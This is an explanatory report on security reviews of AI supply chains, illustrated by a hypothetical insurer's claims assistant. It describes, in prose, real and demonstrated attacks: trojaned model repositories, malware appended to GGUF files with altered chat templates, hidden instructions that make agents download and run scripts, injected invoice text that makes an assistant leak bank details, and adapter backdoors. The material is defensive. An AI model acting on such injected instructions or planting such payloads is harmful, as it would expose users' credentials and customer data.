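# Security risks from reused pretrained models, shared prompts and internal AI applications

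## What organisations reuse and what a supply-chain review checks

In a supply-chain review of an AI system, an organisation examines the parts it took from elsewhere, and the parts its teams copy from one another, before deciding whether to use them. The practice comes from software security, where companies track the outside code in their products. AI systems contain a lot of such code. In *The Grand Software Supply Chain of AI Systems*, Cesarano and Monperrus (2026) assembled a reference system from 48 open-source projects and found that it pulls in 11,508 packages, with about 392 million lines in total. AI systems also depend on models and on instructions in everyday language, which can do harm in ways that inspecting code will not reveal.

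### From a public model to a company's assistant

A language model takes in text and produces more text. Its output depends on its weights, the numbers (often billions of them) that training adjusts. Training a model from scratch costs so much that few organisations do it. The rest start from a pretrained model, one that someone else has trained. An open-weight model is one whose developer has published the weights, so a company can download it and run it on its own machines.

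Some organisations use a pretrained model as it is, and others adapt it first. *Software Dependencies 2.0* (2025), a study of how open-source projects build on pretrained models, found both practices. Fine-tuning continues the training on a smaller set of examples, such as a company's past correspondence, and can change every weight. Training an adapter costs less. The original weights stay fixed, and training produces only a small file of extra weights, which the software combines with the originals when the model runs. An adapter must be used with the exact version of the base model it was made for, and Cesarano and Monperrus warn that a different version gives undefined behaviour. Quantization, a form of compression, stores each weight less precisely so that the model needs less memory, but makes the model somewhat less accurate.

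Each of these operations produces a new file, often from a new publisher. People mostly share these files through model hubs, which are public sites for uploading and downloading models. Hugging Face runs the dominant one. In late October 2026 its *Models* page listed 3,192,960 models, many of them altered copies of others. Constellation Research, quoting Hugging Face's figures, put the number derived from Alibaba's Qwen family at 151,448. DeepSeek, a Chinese developer, had 117,000 downloads on Hugging Face for its own release of V4.1 Flash, while a compressed version from a different account, ISTA-DASLab, had 1.38 million. A team that believes it is running a DeepSeek model may well be running a file that DeepSeek did not publish.

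Ajibode, Ben Sghaier and colleagues (2026), in *When Model Release Meets Model Reuse*, surveyed 95 developers whose software uses models from Hugging Face. Only 31.4% traced a model's origin beyond its immediate parent. Only 18.9% listed security flaws among their top three worries, while 42.1% listed models that perform worse than advertised. About one in twenty of the developers invited took part, so the percentages are rough.

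To turn a model into an application, developers give it a system prompt, standing instructions that it receives before the user's message. A chat template, a small script often shipped with the model, arranges all the messages into the text the model reads. Many applications add retrieval. Software splits the company's documents into passages, converts each passage into a list of numbers that reflects its meaning, and stores the lists in an index. When a question comes in, the software finds the passages closest to it in meaning and adds them to the model's input. If developers also let the model use tools, it becomes an agent. The model writes a request in a fixed format, and a program carries it out, for example by searching a database, sending an email or running a command on a computer. The result goes back to the model, which may then make another request.

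Instructions, retrieved documents and tool outputs all reach the model as text. This allows prompt injection, in which an outsider adds text to the input that makes the model follow their instructions. According to *Inference-Time Backdoors via Chat Templates* (2026), models cannot reliably tell authoritative instructions from the contents of a retrieved document or a tool's output.

A hypothetical insurer has built a claims assistant. Its engineers downloaded an open-weight model and an adapter for insurance correspondence from the same hub. They copied the system prompt that another department had left in the company's prompt library. The assistant retrieves text from 200,000 internal documents: policies, old claims, and letters and invoices that claimants sent in. For now, claims handlers ask the assistant questions and read its answers. Their department would also like it to send letters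 to policyholders, which would make it an agent.

### Three routes to harm

A reused part can do harm if a file runs code on the computer, the weights produce harmful behaviour, or text leads the model to misuse its access.

Some model files, most often those in Python's pickle format, can run code when they are opened. A model's repository, the folder in which its publisher keeps the files, can also include scripts. The Hacker News' *Fake OpenAI Privacy Filter Repo Hits #1 on Hugging Face* (2026) describes a case from May 2026. Someone copied the description of an OpenAI tool for removing personal data from text, almost word for word, and published it under a similar name with a script that was supposedly for starting the model. On Windows machines, the script downloaded a program that took screenshots and stole browser data and cryptocurrency wallets. If one of the insurer's engineers had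 run a similar script, the company could have lost credentials before anyone used its assistant.

An attack through the weights runs no foreign code. The model calculates an answer from its weights as usual, but the answer is harmful. Reviewers worry most about backdoors, which are behaviours that appear only when a particular trigger is present. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) points out that an adapter is enough to introduce a backdoor, since it can change what the model does without altering the base weights. The insurer's adapter might summarise claims well for months, and then describe any claim that contains a certain odd phrase as unproblematic.

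An attacker can also use text alone, without a malicious file or altered weights. Suppose a claimant submits a repair invoice with an instruction in tiny print telling the assistant to include other customers' bank details in its summary. The invoice joins the 200,000 documents, the assistant retrieves it, and the model follows the instruction. The damage depends on the model's access. If the assistant only answers staff, the details appear on a claims handler's screen, but if it can also send letters, they could go to the claimant. An instruction hidden in a copied system prompt or a doctored chat template can have the same effect in every conversation.

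Other taxonomies are more detailed. The *Cisco Integrated AI Security and Safety Framework Report* (2025) lists 22 types of supply-chain threat in four groups, one of which includes both code execution and hidden triggers in model files. For a reviewer, those two belong in separate groups because they require different checks. Guidance from the Australian Signals Directorate (2025), a government cyber security agency, has a separate question for each, one on whether a saved model is compromised and another on whether anyone has maliciously modified the model itself.

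The checks cannot replace one another because they examine different things at different times. A scanner inspects files for code that the computer would execute. Weights are not executable code, so a backdoored model passes the scan. Using safetensors, a file format that holds only numbers and descriptive data, does not prevent this. *Model-as-a-Trojan* (2026) argues that no scanner could detect such a backdoor, since a conditional behaviour in the weights looks like any other ability until its trigger appears. Testing the model's answers can miss malicious code in the file, because the answers may look entirely normal, and the code will already have run when the model was loaded for testing.

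Prompts are easier to check in one respect, because people can read them. Cesarano and Monperrus distinguish parts whose behaviour a reader can work out from their contents, such as prompt templates and scripts, from trained parts such as weights and adapters, where nobody can do this. But reading the insurer's system prompt carefully does not protect against malicious instructions in an invoice that arrives next week. Checking a file's hash, a short fingerprint calculated from its contents, also has limits, because a match proves only that the file is unchanged. If an attacker inserted a backdoor before publication, the published hash will match the backdoored file.

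A case from November 2026 shows how attackers can exploit gaps between checks. *Скачанные нейросети сами предлагают запустить троян* (2026), published by the Russian technology site iXBT, reports that a security specialist named Düzgün checked 3.27 million public repositories on Hugging Face and found five malicious ones. In the main campaign, the attackers appended a Windows program to a model file in GGUF, a common format for running models on a personal computer. Software that loads such files ignores anything after the weights, so nothing ran at loading and the model chatted normally. The attackers had also altered the chat template so that each reply began with a command that, if the user ran it, extracted and started the hidden program. A check only for code that executes at loading would miss this attack, as would a test of the model with its original template. In three other repositories,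 hidden instructions were meant to make AI agents with command-line access download and run a script themselves.

### The steps of a review

The order of a review follows largely from these differences.

| Step | What it involves | Who usually does it |
|---|---|---|
| List | Write down every model, adapter, prompt, document collection and tool in the system | The engineers who built it, at management's request |
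| Trace origin | Find out who published each part, what it derives from, and whether the company's copy is the published one | Engineers and security staff |
| Scan | Inspect the files for harmful code without loading them | Security staff |
| Load safely | Open the model in isolation, with settings that refuse to run code | Engineers |
| Test | Give the model chosen inputs and look for harmful behaviour | Engineers and security testers |
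| Examine prompts and application | Read the prompts and templates; establish what the model can reach and who can put text in front of it | The application's team and security staff |
| Rate | Judge how likely each harm is, how bad it would be, and how good the evidence is | Security staff and the department that owns the system |
| Decide | Approve, restrict, replace or reject | The manager who answers for the system |

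Job titles vary, and in a small company one person may do most of this. The allocation broadly fits the duties in Coalition for Secure AI's *Establish Risks and Controls for the AI Supply Chain, V 1.0* (2025), a paper from an industry group, although it does not use these eight steps. The paper says executives should find out where the organisation already uses AI and set up a group with security, legal, technical and business members. Security staff should verify the integrity of models and write the rules on which risks the organisation accepts. The paper also notes that the engineers who know most about how a model works may not know much about how someone would attack it.

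Reviewers have to scan a model's files before loading them, and load the model before testing it. They can review the prompts later or in parallel, though for the claims assistant there is a case for starting with them, since reading one page of instructions takes minutes. Approval covers only the exact files examined, not later files published under the same name. According to 黃 (2026), in *免費本地AI藏致命木馬*, a report for the Hong Kong news site HK01, the attackers in the main November campaign first published clean models, waited for downloads to build up, and changed the chat templates only on 26 November. A company that had reviewed one of these models a week earlier and then accepted the update would have had a malicious model despite the clean review.

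### Levels of evidence

Four levels of evidence separate what has happened from what could happen, which reports about AI security tend to mix. A risk is *demonstrated* when researchers have made the attack work in their own tests. It is *found in circulation* when someone discovers a real instance where others could obtain it. It is *used against a victim* when the attack has harmed an identifiable person or organisation. It is *measured as a loss* when someone has quantified that harm in money, records or days of interrupted work.

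A risk's rating can rise as new evidence appears. In July 2025 Pillar Security (2025), which sells AI security and so has an interest in the result, announced a demonstration in which its researchers planted instructions in the chat templates of GGUF files. Sixteen months later Düzgün found templates of this kind that attackers had put on the hub. Neither iXBT nor HK01 names anyone whose computer was infected, so the risk is rated "found in circulation".

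At the next level, Hugging Face itself suffered a breach in July 2026. The Indian Express' *Hugging Face confirms data breach by AI agent* reports that a malicious dataset on the platform exploited flaws in the company's data processing, ran code on its servers and gave access to internal credentials. Hugging Face found no sign that anyone had altered its public models. OpenAI's incident report of August 2026 concluded that a swarm of its own agents had probably carried out the attack.

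Measured losses are much harder to find. The Australian Signals Directorate cites one survey in which around 65% of organisations had been affected by an AI-related data leak, and another in which 13% reported breaches of their AI systems. These percentages are shares of respondents and don't measure how much anyone lost.

A low level can mean either that the risk is small or that nobody has a good way to detect it. Düzgün's search for hidden programs and suspicious instructions covered millions of repositories, but it would have missed a backdoor in a model's weights.

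Counts of bad models need similar care. A *flagged model* is one that a scanner has reported, whether or not it is harmful. A *malicious model* is one shown to contain something put there to harm its user. A *harmed user* is a person or organisation that suffered the damage. In early 2024 the security company JFrog reported on roughly a hundred models on Hugging Face with hidden actions. Cesarano and Monperrus describe all of them as carrying malicious payloads. *Hugging Face – GitHub для ИИ*, from the Russian news site Ferra.ru, reports that most looked like harmless proofs of concept and that JFrog's researchers judged ten to be truly malicious. By that account, about a hundred models were flagged and ten were malicious. The number of harmed users is unknown.

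Download counts do not show how many people opened or ran a malicious file. The fake Privacy Filter repository showed about 244,000 downloads within 18 hours, and The Hacker News reports a suspicion that someone inflated the number to make the repository look trustworthy. Even an accurate count includes people who never opened the file. According to 黃, the five November models had reached 2,807 downloads when Hugging Face removed them. In the main campaign, a download did nothing until the user ran the command.

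## Listing models, prompts and applications, and reading suppliers' documents

A review starts with a list of what the company already runs. The insurer knows about its claims assistant because a department asked for it, but it may not know about a script that one of its actuaries uses to summarise reports, or a writing assistant that a software supplier switched on in its last update. Once the reviewers have a list, they need details of each part, many of which only its supplier can provide.

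### Finding what is in use

No single record covers every model, prompt and application, so reviewers compare several. Two of them, the records of packages and containers, come from ordinary software management. A package is ready-made code that programmers install, and a container bundles a program with everything it needs to run.

| Record | How it reveals AI use | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
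| Code search | Finds commands that load models, file endings such as .safetensors and .gguf, and the web addresses of model providers | Programs outside the company's shared code store; model names kept in a database or settings file; prompts that staff typed into a web tool |
| Package and container records | List installed libraries for running or calling models | Which model a program uses, if it downloads the model on starting |
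| Network logs | Show which machines contacted a model hub or provider | The model's name and the prompt, which encryption hides from an ordinary log; models copied between company machines; work on home networks |
| Purchasing records | Show subscriptions and invoices from AI suppliers | Free models; AI features in products the company already pays for |
| Staff declarations | Explain what people use, for what purpose and with what data | Anything people have forgotten, don't recognise as AI, or would rather not admit |

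These strengths and gaps are inferred from how each record is created, not from measured detection rates. Some gaps are easy to narrow. Even when encryption hides a model's name, the size of a transfer is a clue, because eight billion weights stored at two bytes each take up about 16 gigabytes. The Australian Signals Directorate advises organisations to ask about any AI features that suppliers add to products the organisations already own.

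Prompts are the easiest part to miss because they are ordinary sentences, with no fixed command to search for. The claims team took its prompt from the company's prompt library, which can show which prompts it holds but may not show who has copied them. The reviewers therefore have to ask each team for the prompt its application is using now, which may differ from the one in the library.

Comparing the lists also gives a rough estimate of how many applications are missing from both. Suppose staff declare 30 applications, 24 appear in the network logs, and 18 are on both lists. The logs then include 18 of the 30 declared applications, or 60%. If they include the same share of the undeclared ones, the company has about 40 applications, of which 36 are on at least one list and about 4 are on neither. Ecologists estimate animal populations in the same way. The calculation assumes that being on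 one list doesn't make an application more or less likely to be on the other, which is doubtful here. A downloaded model that an employee runs offline without telling anyone is missing from both lists, so the real number is probably above 40.

When a company trains its own model, software can collect the details during the work. *AIGen* (2026) describes a tool that uses a language model to turn training records, code and project notes into inventory entries. Its developers tried it on eight open-source projects, including one for reading chest X-rays and one for predicting air quality, and rated the 124 entries it produced. They judged 59% free of errors and another 32% good with minor omissions, while the remaining 9% or so had large gaps or factual mistakes. Descriptions were the hardest part to get right. The developers were rating their own tool, and none of the examples they name closely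 resembles an assistant assembled from downloaded parts.

### What goes into a bill of materials

A spreadsheet is enough for a first list. With a machine-readable format, software can search every system for a model that someone has reported as bad. For ordinary programs, such a list is called a software bill of materials, and an AI bill of materials adds the models and data. Friedman and Leiserson (2026) insist in *Driving AI Transparency*, a policy memo from the Institute for Security and Technology, that the AI list must include or accompany the ordinary one. Otherwise it would leave out the software that runs the model and connects it to tools.

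Most organisations that exchange these lists use either CycloneDX, from OWASP (a non-profit foundation for software security), or SPDX, from the Linux Foundation. Companies often choose SPDX to track licences and origins and CycloneDX to manage security flaws, according to *Building an Open AIBOM Standard in the Wild* (Rajbahadur, Gallaba and colleagues, 2025).

In CycloneDX, every part of a system is a component with a name, a version, a licence and an identifier that software can look up. A model has the type "machine-learning-model" and a `modelCard` section for its training data, settings and limitations. Other entries link to its source code, research paper and download location. CycloneDX has released version 1.7 and announced a version 2.0 with more support for agents. In March 2026, the project also published a guide to these lists, the *Authoritative Guide to AI/ML BOM*.

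SPDX 3.0, released in April 2024, covers the same ground in two profiles, or sets of fields. The AI profile describes a model's identity, licence, architecture, training and known risks. The Dataset profile describes the data's source, processing and intended use, and any biases or sensitive information it contains. Rajbahadur and colleagues, who helped to write the specification, report that the working group considered 103 fields and chose 20 for the AI profile and 18 for the Dataset profile. Only five of the AI fields and six of the Dataset fields are compulsory, and the group chose these partly because real projects were likely to have the information. A valid SPDX file may therefore leave out the details a security reviewer most wants.

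Governments have tried to define what every list should contain. In May 2026 the G7 Cybersecurity Working Group (2026), a group of national cyber security agencies, published about 50 voluntary "minimum elements" in seven groups, ranging from a model's hash to the system's uptime. Friedman and Leiserson object that a voluntary list cannot serve as a minimum, and that some entries, such as "security controls", are too open-ended for two companies to fill in the same way. They contrast the G7 list with one for ordinary software that a US government agency published in 2021, which set out what a bill of materials needed to serve its purpose. CISA's *2026 Minimum Elements for a Software Bill of Materials (SBOM)* (2026) has since updated and replaced the 2021 list.

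The memo itself proposes a shorter list for models: name, version, other identifiers, hash, licence, supplier, original creator, parent models and supporting documents. The supplier is whoever the company got the model from, and the creator is whoever first trained or published it. These are often different on Hugging Face, as with the compressed DeepSeek model, so the list needs a separate field for each.

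A short bill of materials for the claims assistant might look like this.

| Part | Version on record | Obtained from | Created by | Derived from | Still unknown |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Language model | Hub revision and file hash | Hub account A | A well-known developer | The developer's release, compressed by account A | What the training data contained |
| Adapter | Hub revision and file hash | Hub account B | Account B | The same language model, version not stated | Who runs account B; whose letters it trained on; licence |
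| Chat template | Hash of the template | Hub account A | Probably the developer | The developer's template | Whether account A changed it |
| Retrieval model | Hub revision and file hash | The developer's own account | The same developer | None stated | What the training data contained |
| System prompt | Revision 7 and hash of the text | Company prompt library | Complaints department, then the claims team | Revision 3 of the complaints prompt | Who made revisions 4 to 6 |
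| Document index | Date built and number of documents | Policy and claims systems | Staff, claimants and repairers | 200,000 documents | Which documents outsiders wrote |

The engineers would probably have named two models, the language model and the adapter, but a third converts the company's documents into the lists of numbers that retrieval depends on. The chat template has its own line because many publishers keep it in a separate file, where someone could alter it without changing the hash of the weights.

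The last column may be the most useful. Friedman and Leiserson want organisations to record missing information explicitly, as "known unknowns", because a blank could also mean that nobody looked. The adapter has the most gaps, and the insurer can also use the column as a list of questions for the next steps.

Neither the G7's elements nor the memo's core fields have an entry for system prompts. But CycloneDX can describe configurations as well as models and code, so the insurer can record its prompt as a configuration, with a version, a hash and a link to the text. The line about revision 3 is worth recording too. If the complaints department finds that its prompt reveals too much about customers and corrects it, the claims team will keep using the old wording unless someone can see that the claims prompt came from the complaints prompt.

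A bill of materials can show what a system contains, but even a complete one cannot fully capture what the system is doing at a particular moment, as Friedman and Leiserson point out. An agent may fetch outside data, act with an employee's permissions and disappear when its task is done. The G7 group considered adding an element for how much a system decides on its own, but left it out because its members' laws may treat the matter differently. If the claims assistant started sending letters, the change would not appear in the table unless the company listed the new email tool.

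### What reviewers ask of suppliers

A company with a contract can ask the supplier to fill the gaps. The Australian Signals Directorate recommends settling this early and writing the answers into the agreement. Its suggestions include limits on using the customer's data for training, a right to audit, rules on where data is kept, plans for keeping the service running, and a clear division of responsibilities.

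Friedman and Leiserson describe two further requests. A customer can ask whether a newly discovered problem affects the supplier's product and what the supplier is doing about it, or whether the product contains a particular component or anything from a particular source. For instance, after Hugging Face removed the five malicious repositories in November 2026, the insurer could have asked each of its software suppliers whether they had ever used any of them. A supplier without an inventory would have had to guess or start searching.

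Some questions have a legal basis in the EU's AI Act, which requires technical documentation for high-risk systems, covering their software components, training methods and data, though it does not specifically require an AI bill of materials. The payment card industry's security standard already requires an inventory of custom software and the outside components in it, and Friedman and Leiserson think a similar rule could easily cover models and data.

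Suppliers often decline to say what data a model was trained on. Many of the largest commercial developers treat this as a trade secret, so the information is missing for some of the most widely used models. A customer can instead ask for a signed statement, for example that the developer collected no data in breach of European privacy law. The customer can use the statement in a dispute but cannot check whether it is true.

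The insurer can work from several standard documents. OWASP includes the supply chain in its list of the main risks to applications built on language models. The US standards institute NIST has added AI practices to its framework for secure software development in SP 800-218A. The Cloud Security Alliance, an industry association, offers an AI questionnaire for suppliers to complete, but the answers are only the supplier's own account unless someone checks them. A supplier may also hold a certificate under ISO/IEC 42001, the international standard for managing AI in an organisation. The certificate concerns the organisation's procedures, so it does not show whether a particular model file is safe.

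Two of the guidance documents are especially detailed on controls, and two on what to record. They differ in how they treat models, prompts and applications that a company builds for itself.

| Document | Models | Prompts | In-house applications |
|---|---|---|---|
| Coalition for Secure AI, June 2025 | Keep tamper-proof records of origin, sign model files, use formats that cannot run code, and refuse models without proper records | Filter outside data for injected instructions | Record filters, retrieval parts, tools, access rights and dependencies |
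| Australian Signals Directorate, October 2025 | Use trusted sources, check hashes or signatures, use safe formats, test and monitor | Treats injection as one possible effect of poisoned data | Keep a software bill of materials, scan for malware, limit access |
| G7 Cybersecurity Working Group, May 2026 | Record identity, hash, producer, parent models, training and licence | No element for system prompts | Record components, producer, version, data flows and purpose |
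| Friedman and Leiserson, June 2026 | Record the shorter core set of fields, with unknowns marked | No field for system prompts | Include the software for agents and tool connections |

Models get the most attention in all four documents. The Coalition for Secure AI covers applications most thoroughly. It wants a company to record the version and settings of every filter, how the retrieval system keeps different customers' data apart, and every tool and outside system the model can reach. Reviewers of the claims assistant could use that list almost as it stands. But the list omits the system prompt, and the coalition's advice on prompts deals with what outsiders put into the data. An insurer that followed all four documents could still run a copied prompt that nobody had entered in an inventory.

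The coalition also warns against trusting a model just because it is kept in-house. Someone with access to the company's storage could alter the weights and leave few traces, so the same signatures and access limits should apply there. The same applies to the insurer's prompt library, where an employee can change a sentence without technical skill.

All of this advice is based on expert judgement. The coalition's tables list a threat, a control and the harm that might follow, but not how often the control works. The Australian Signals Directorate acknowledges that the effectiveness of AI security tools can be hard to verify. Reasoning alone is enough to justify some controls, such as comparing hashes. Questionnaires and inventories depend on people answering accurately and then acting on the answers, which is much less certain.

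### How complete the documents are

The insurer downloaded its language model and adapter without a contract for either. It has only a model card, the page on which a publisher describes a model's purpose, training data, test results and limitations. Publishers write their own cards, which may contain anything from a full account to a single line.

In *A Large-Scale Measurement of AI Bill of Materials Completeness in Hugging Face*, Erfan, Ryan and Rahman (2026) measured how much of a bill of materials can be filled in from what publishers provide. They collected records of 2,942,466 public models and kept those with more than 100 downloads. They then used OWASP's generator, which reads a model's public page and files, to produce 97,940 bills of materials in CycloneDX format.

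| Information | Share of the 97,940 lists that had it |
|---|---|
| Licence | 73.14% |
| Link to source code | 58.70% |
| Training or other datasets | 39.35% |
| Technical limitations | 16.74% |
| Research paper | 13.50% |
| Safety-risk assessment | 9.76% |
| Description with real content | 0.22% |
| Intended use | 0% |

Some of these gaps probably come from the generator. Intended use is a standard heading on model cards, but it was missing from all of the nearly 98,000 lists, which suggests that the tool fails to pick it up. Erfan and colleagues accept that the tool's extraction method may affect which fields appear. This may also explain why almost every list had something in the description field but only 211 had more than placeholder text. The figures show what a company would get by running this generator, which may be less than someone would find by reading the page carefully.

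The generator also gives each list a completeness score out of 100, and the average was 54.31. A company might be tempted to set a pass mark, so it matters how the score comes about. The tool works out what share of the fields is present in each of five groups, multiplies each share by a fixed number of points, and adds up the results:

| Group of fields | Points available | Average share present | Average points |
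|---|---|---|---|
| Required structure | 20 | 100% | 20.0 |
| Metadata | 20 | 40% | 8.0 |
| Basic identity and licence | 20 | 81.75% | 16.4 |
| Model card | 30 | 19.51% | 5.9 |
| Links to outside sources | 10 | 68.02% | 6.8 |

That comes to about 57 points, and deductions for missing important fields bring it down to 54. Every list gets the first 20 points, because they are for entries the tool fills in automatically, such as the format's name and the list's serial number. The lowest score in the study was 46.6. A model can therefore score only about eight points below the average even if its publisher explained almost nothing.

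High scores are not reassuring either. The highest score, 68.7, was shared by 269 models, many of them compressed or re-uploaded copies of well-known models. Someone who re-uploads a model can also copy its card, as the attackers behind the fake OpenAI repository did. A check of the text alone would have scored their version about the same as the real one.

A completed field can also be inaccurate. The study recorded whether a field had an entry, but nobody checked whether the named datasets were the ones used. Its published field counts also leave out the model file's hash and the parent model, which are the two fields the insurer needs most. The hash would show whether account A's file is a faithful copy, and the parent model would show which release the adapter belongs to.

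Publishers who linked a research paper and named a dataset also tended to document other things. Technical limitations were listed for 49.04% of their models and source code was linked for 99.59%, compared with 7.16% and 55.04% of models with neither a paper nor a dataset. A reviewer short of time could look harder at models that lack both, although the study does not connect poor documentation with malicious models. It also provides little information about models with few downloads or those that a company keeps to itself. Text generation accounts for 82,591 of the lists, so the totals mostly describe language models.

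There is less evidence on whether people can use the finished documents. Rajbahadur and colleagues interviewed ten practitioners about the SPDX fields and tried the fields out at one multinational company. The fields covered the company's ethics and legal checklists, and software could fill in some of them for models from outside the company. The interviewees found the fields relevant but pointed out gaps. These results are encouraging, but they come from the people who wrote the specification. They concern whether the information fits a company's procedures and do not show that a bill of materials helps a company find a compromised model sooner.

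The insurer then has to decide what missing information to accept. If it followed the Coalition for Secure AI strictly, it would refuse every model without proper records of origin, including its own adapter and a large share of the others on the hub. It could instead accept gaps that the rest of the review can make up for. Undisclosed training data is nearly unavoidable with a popular model, but the insurer can at least test how the model behaves. An adapter from an unidentified account, with no stated parent version and no licence, is harder to justify, especially if the claims team could train one on its own letters.

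## Checking where a model came from

The insurer's bill of materials lists an account and a file hash for each model, but the engineers may not have downloaded what they intended. They might have picked a look-alike name, or used the right name after someone else had taken it over. An intruder might also have replaced a file without changing its name, either through the publisher's account or by breaking into the hub. Reviewers need to rule out these possibilities before they rely on anything the publisher has written about the model.

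### Look-alike names

Hugging Face identifies each model by its publisher's account name followed by the model's name, as in `Author/ModelName`. Anyone can register an account name that isn't taken. Attackers have long exploited the same rule in code registries by typosquatting, which means publishing a package under a slight misspelling of a popular name and waiting for a programmer to mistype it. *TypoSmart* (2025), which covers typosquatting across several registries, notes that attackers also do this on Hugging Face, with models named after famous ones.

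Because the full name consists of an account name and a model name, an attacker can copy the model name exactly and change only the account name. Some changes are hard to see. In *What enables malicious models?*, zabuqasem mentions that Hugging Face's font makes the digit 1 and a lowercase L look similar.

An attacker can also pose as the company by opening an organisation account in its name and inviting its engineers to join. According to zabuqasem, the invitation appears to come from Hugging Face's domain. An engineer who accepts could then store the company's models where the attacker can alter them. 5stars217 (2024), a security researcher who has used malicious models in attack exercises, argues in *Practicalities of Malicious Models* that such attacks are feasible mainly because of how organisation accounts work.

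Software that looks for misspelled package names is less useful for models. *I see models being a whole other thing* (2023), a study of naming habits, explains that a small change to a package's name is a warning sign, whereas model publishers routinely make such changes to show a new size, version or format. Flagging every small change would make a detector useless, but ignoring them would let through an attacker who followed the convention. The study identified no typosquatting incidents on Hugging Face at the time.

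By 2025, researchers had compared the names of models and datasets on Hugging Face with those of the 100 most popular in each category, and had also looked for imitations among organisation names.

| Examined | Number | Suspected look-alikes | Closer inspection |
|---|---|---|---|
| Models | 1,020,755 | 1,574 | 10.4% had suspicious and harmful features |
| Datasets | 219,812 | 625 | 42.2% showed signs of deliberate impersonation, judging from a sample |
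| Organisations | 127,011 | 302 | 4.8% showed explicit malicious intent |

The percentages work out at about 164 models, or roughly one in every 6,000, and 14 or 15 organisations. "Suspicious and harmful features" is a looser standard than proof that a model was built to harm its user. However, a comparison with only the 100 most downloaded models misses imitations of all others, including any specialised model an insurer might want. The figures also don't measure how many people downloaded one of these models by mistake.

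### The false Privacy Filter and the value of popularity

OpenAI released its Privacy Filter in April 2026, according to The Hacker News. An imitation appeared on Hugging Face under the account name Open-OSS, which a hurried engineer might take for OpenAI's open-source division. HiddenLayer, the security company that found the imitation on 7 May, reports in *Malware Found in Trending Hugging Face Repository "Open-OSS/privacy-filter"* (2026) that the imitation's model card was copied from the original and even linked to OpenAI's real documentation. The copied card differed only in telling users to download the repository and run either `start.bat` or `loader.py`.

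The second of these files began with decoy code that printed false training results. It then called a function whose name suggested that it checked the integrity of the files. The function instead turned off a security check on web connections and fetched a command from a public text-sharing site. The attackers could change that command at any time without touching the repository, so a company that had recorded the hash of every file would still not have known what the downloader would fetch later.

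The repository had 244,000 downloads and 667 likes, and it reached first place on Hugging Face's trending list. HiddenLayer believes that someone almost certainly inflated both the downloads and the likes, but its evidence is stronger for the likes. Of the 667 accounts that liked the repository, 504 had names consisting of a first name, a surname and three digits, and another 153 had names consisting of an adjective, a noun and four digits. Only ten fit neither pattern. HiddenLayer's report doesn't include a similar breakdown of the downloads or estimate how many were genuine or how many computers were infected.

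A model may be popular because somebody paid for a batch of accounts or wrote a script that downloads the same file repeatedly. Its high ranking then attracts real users, whose downloads are indistinguishable from the fake ones. A longer publishing record is harder to fake, though the attackers in November 2026 got around this by publishing clean models first and waiting. Popularity may help in one way, since a security company is more likely to notice a model that many people see, but this doesn't protect people who ran the model before then.

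A better starting point is the developer's own website, where the engineers can follow a link to the hub instead of choosing between similar names in search results. They can also check what else the account has published, and when, although a clean history proves little. HiddenLayer traced some of the accounts that had liked the false Privacy Filter to a second publisher, `anthfu`, which had uploaded six repositories on 24 April with almost the same loader, one of them called `DeepSeek-V4-Pro`. Checking only the Open-OSS account would not have revealed these repositories.

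### Names that change hands

A correct name can also lead to the wrong model. When a publisher deletes its Hugging Face account, anyone can register the account name again and upload a model under the same account and model name. Programs that still request that name will then download the new owner's file. Saraf and Balassiano (2025) tested this in *Model Namespace Reuse* for Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks.

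If a publisher deletes its Hugging Face account, its model disappears and programs that depend on it stop working, so somebody will probably notice. If the publisher first transfers the model to another account, perhaps after a company takeover, Hugging Face redirects requests from the old name to the new one, and the programs keep working. But once someone else registers the old account name and uploads a model, the redirection ends and those programs receive the new file. Nothing visibly breaks, so engineers have no reason to check the name.

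Saraf and Balassiano tried the attack on two cloud services that offer models from Hugging Face. Google's Vertex AI still listed some models as verified although their publishers' accounts no longer existed. They registered one of those account names and uploaded a model containing code that opened a connection to their servers. When they deployed the model through Vertex AI, the code gave them access to the container that ran it, though the container had limited reach within Google's cloud. The same method worked on Microsoft's Azure AI Foundry, where it gave them the permissions of the machine running the model and a foothold in the customer's cloud environment. They removed the harmful code afterwards.

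Researchers searched GitHub, where programmers share code, and found thousands of projects that referred to models by names that anyone could register. Some of these names were in default settings, example notebooks and documentation, where a search for the usual commands for loading a model could miss them.

This risk is rated "demonstrated" because the attack worked on real services, although the researchers carried it out themselves and did not report finding any criminal use of it. They told Google about the problem in February 2025, and Google now scans daily for models whose publishers have disappeared and blocks their deployment on Vertex AI. The researchers warned that anyone who fetches models by name alone was still at risk. A reviewer needs to check where a cloud catalogue gets its models, because a company that has never used Hugging Face directly may still be running a model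 from there.

### Changed files and hijacked accounts

Even if an account stays with its original owner, the files under a name can change. Software that loads a model by name normally fetches the latest version. Most new versions are legitimate corrections, but someone who steals the publisher's password or access token (a long code that lets a program log in) can upload a harmful one. The account is still genuine, the name is right and the downloads come from real users. zabuqasem warns that serious attackers will target existing popular repositories instead of building new ones, for similar reasons.

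The November 2026 campaign showed that a dishonest publisher can release a malicious update without stealing a password. To the company that downloads it, the update looks the same as one released by an attacker using a stolen password.

### The July 2026 breach of Hugging Face

An intruder in the hub's own systems could in principle alter any model on it. After the July 2026 breach, Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026), published on 16 July, reported "no evidence of tampering" with public models, datasets or Spaces (applications it hosts for users). The company made a stronger claim about its software packages and container images, which it had "verified clean".

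The first claim is weaker than the second because it depends on how thoroughly the company searched, which the statement doesn't describe. The second implies that someone compared the files with what they should contain. Hugging Face could compare each model with hashes recorded before the breach, but the statement doesn't mention this. The company advised users to replace their access tokens as a precaution.

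Hugging Face followed with a technical report on 27 July. According to *Hugging Face publishes the technical timeline of the intrusion* (2026), an account by the IT company noze, Hugging Face now confirmed that the intruder had gained permission to change its source code. A review found no unauthorised changes, and the published packages and container images matched their expected hashes. The report listed customers' models as unaffected. The intruder accessed datasets containing solutions to security challenges, which suggests an aim other than altering models. noze points out that no independent investigator had yet confirmed the findings.

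Dubach points out in *The OpenAI–Hugging Face Incident in Plain English* that finding no unauthorised package does not establish that nobody could have made one. The evidence so far favours Hugging Face's conclusion that its models were untouched, but a customer without its own records from before July is relying on the company's investigation. If the insurer had downloaded a model in June and recorded its hash, it could download the same version again in August and compare the hashes. A match would show that the breach had not altered that model between the two dates, regardless of what Hugging Face had checked.

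### How fixed revisions, hashes and signatures work

A Hugging Face model is stored in a repository that keeps a history of changes. Each saved version, or commit, has a 40-character identifier calculated from its files and its history. Engineers can put this identifier in the command that loads the model:

`from_pretrained("Author/ModelName", revision="abcdef1234567890...")`

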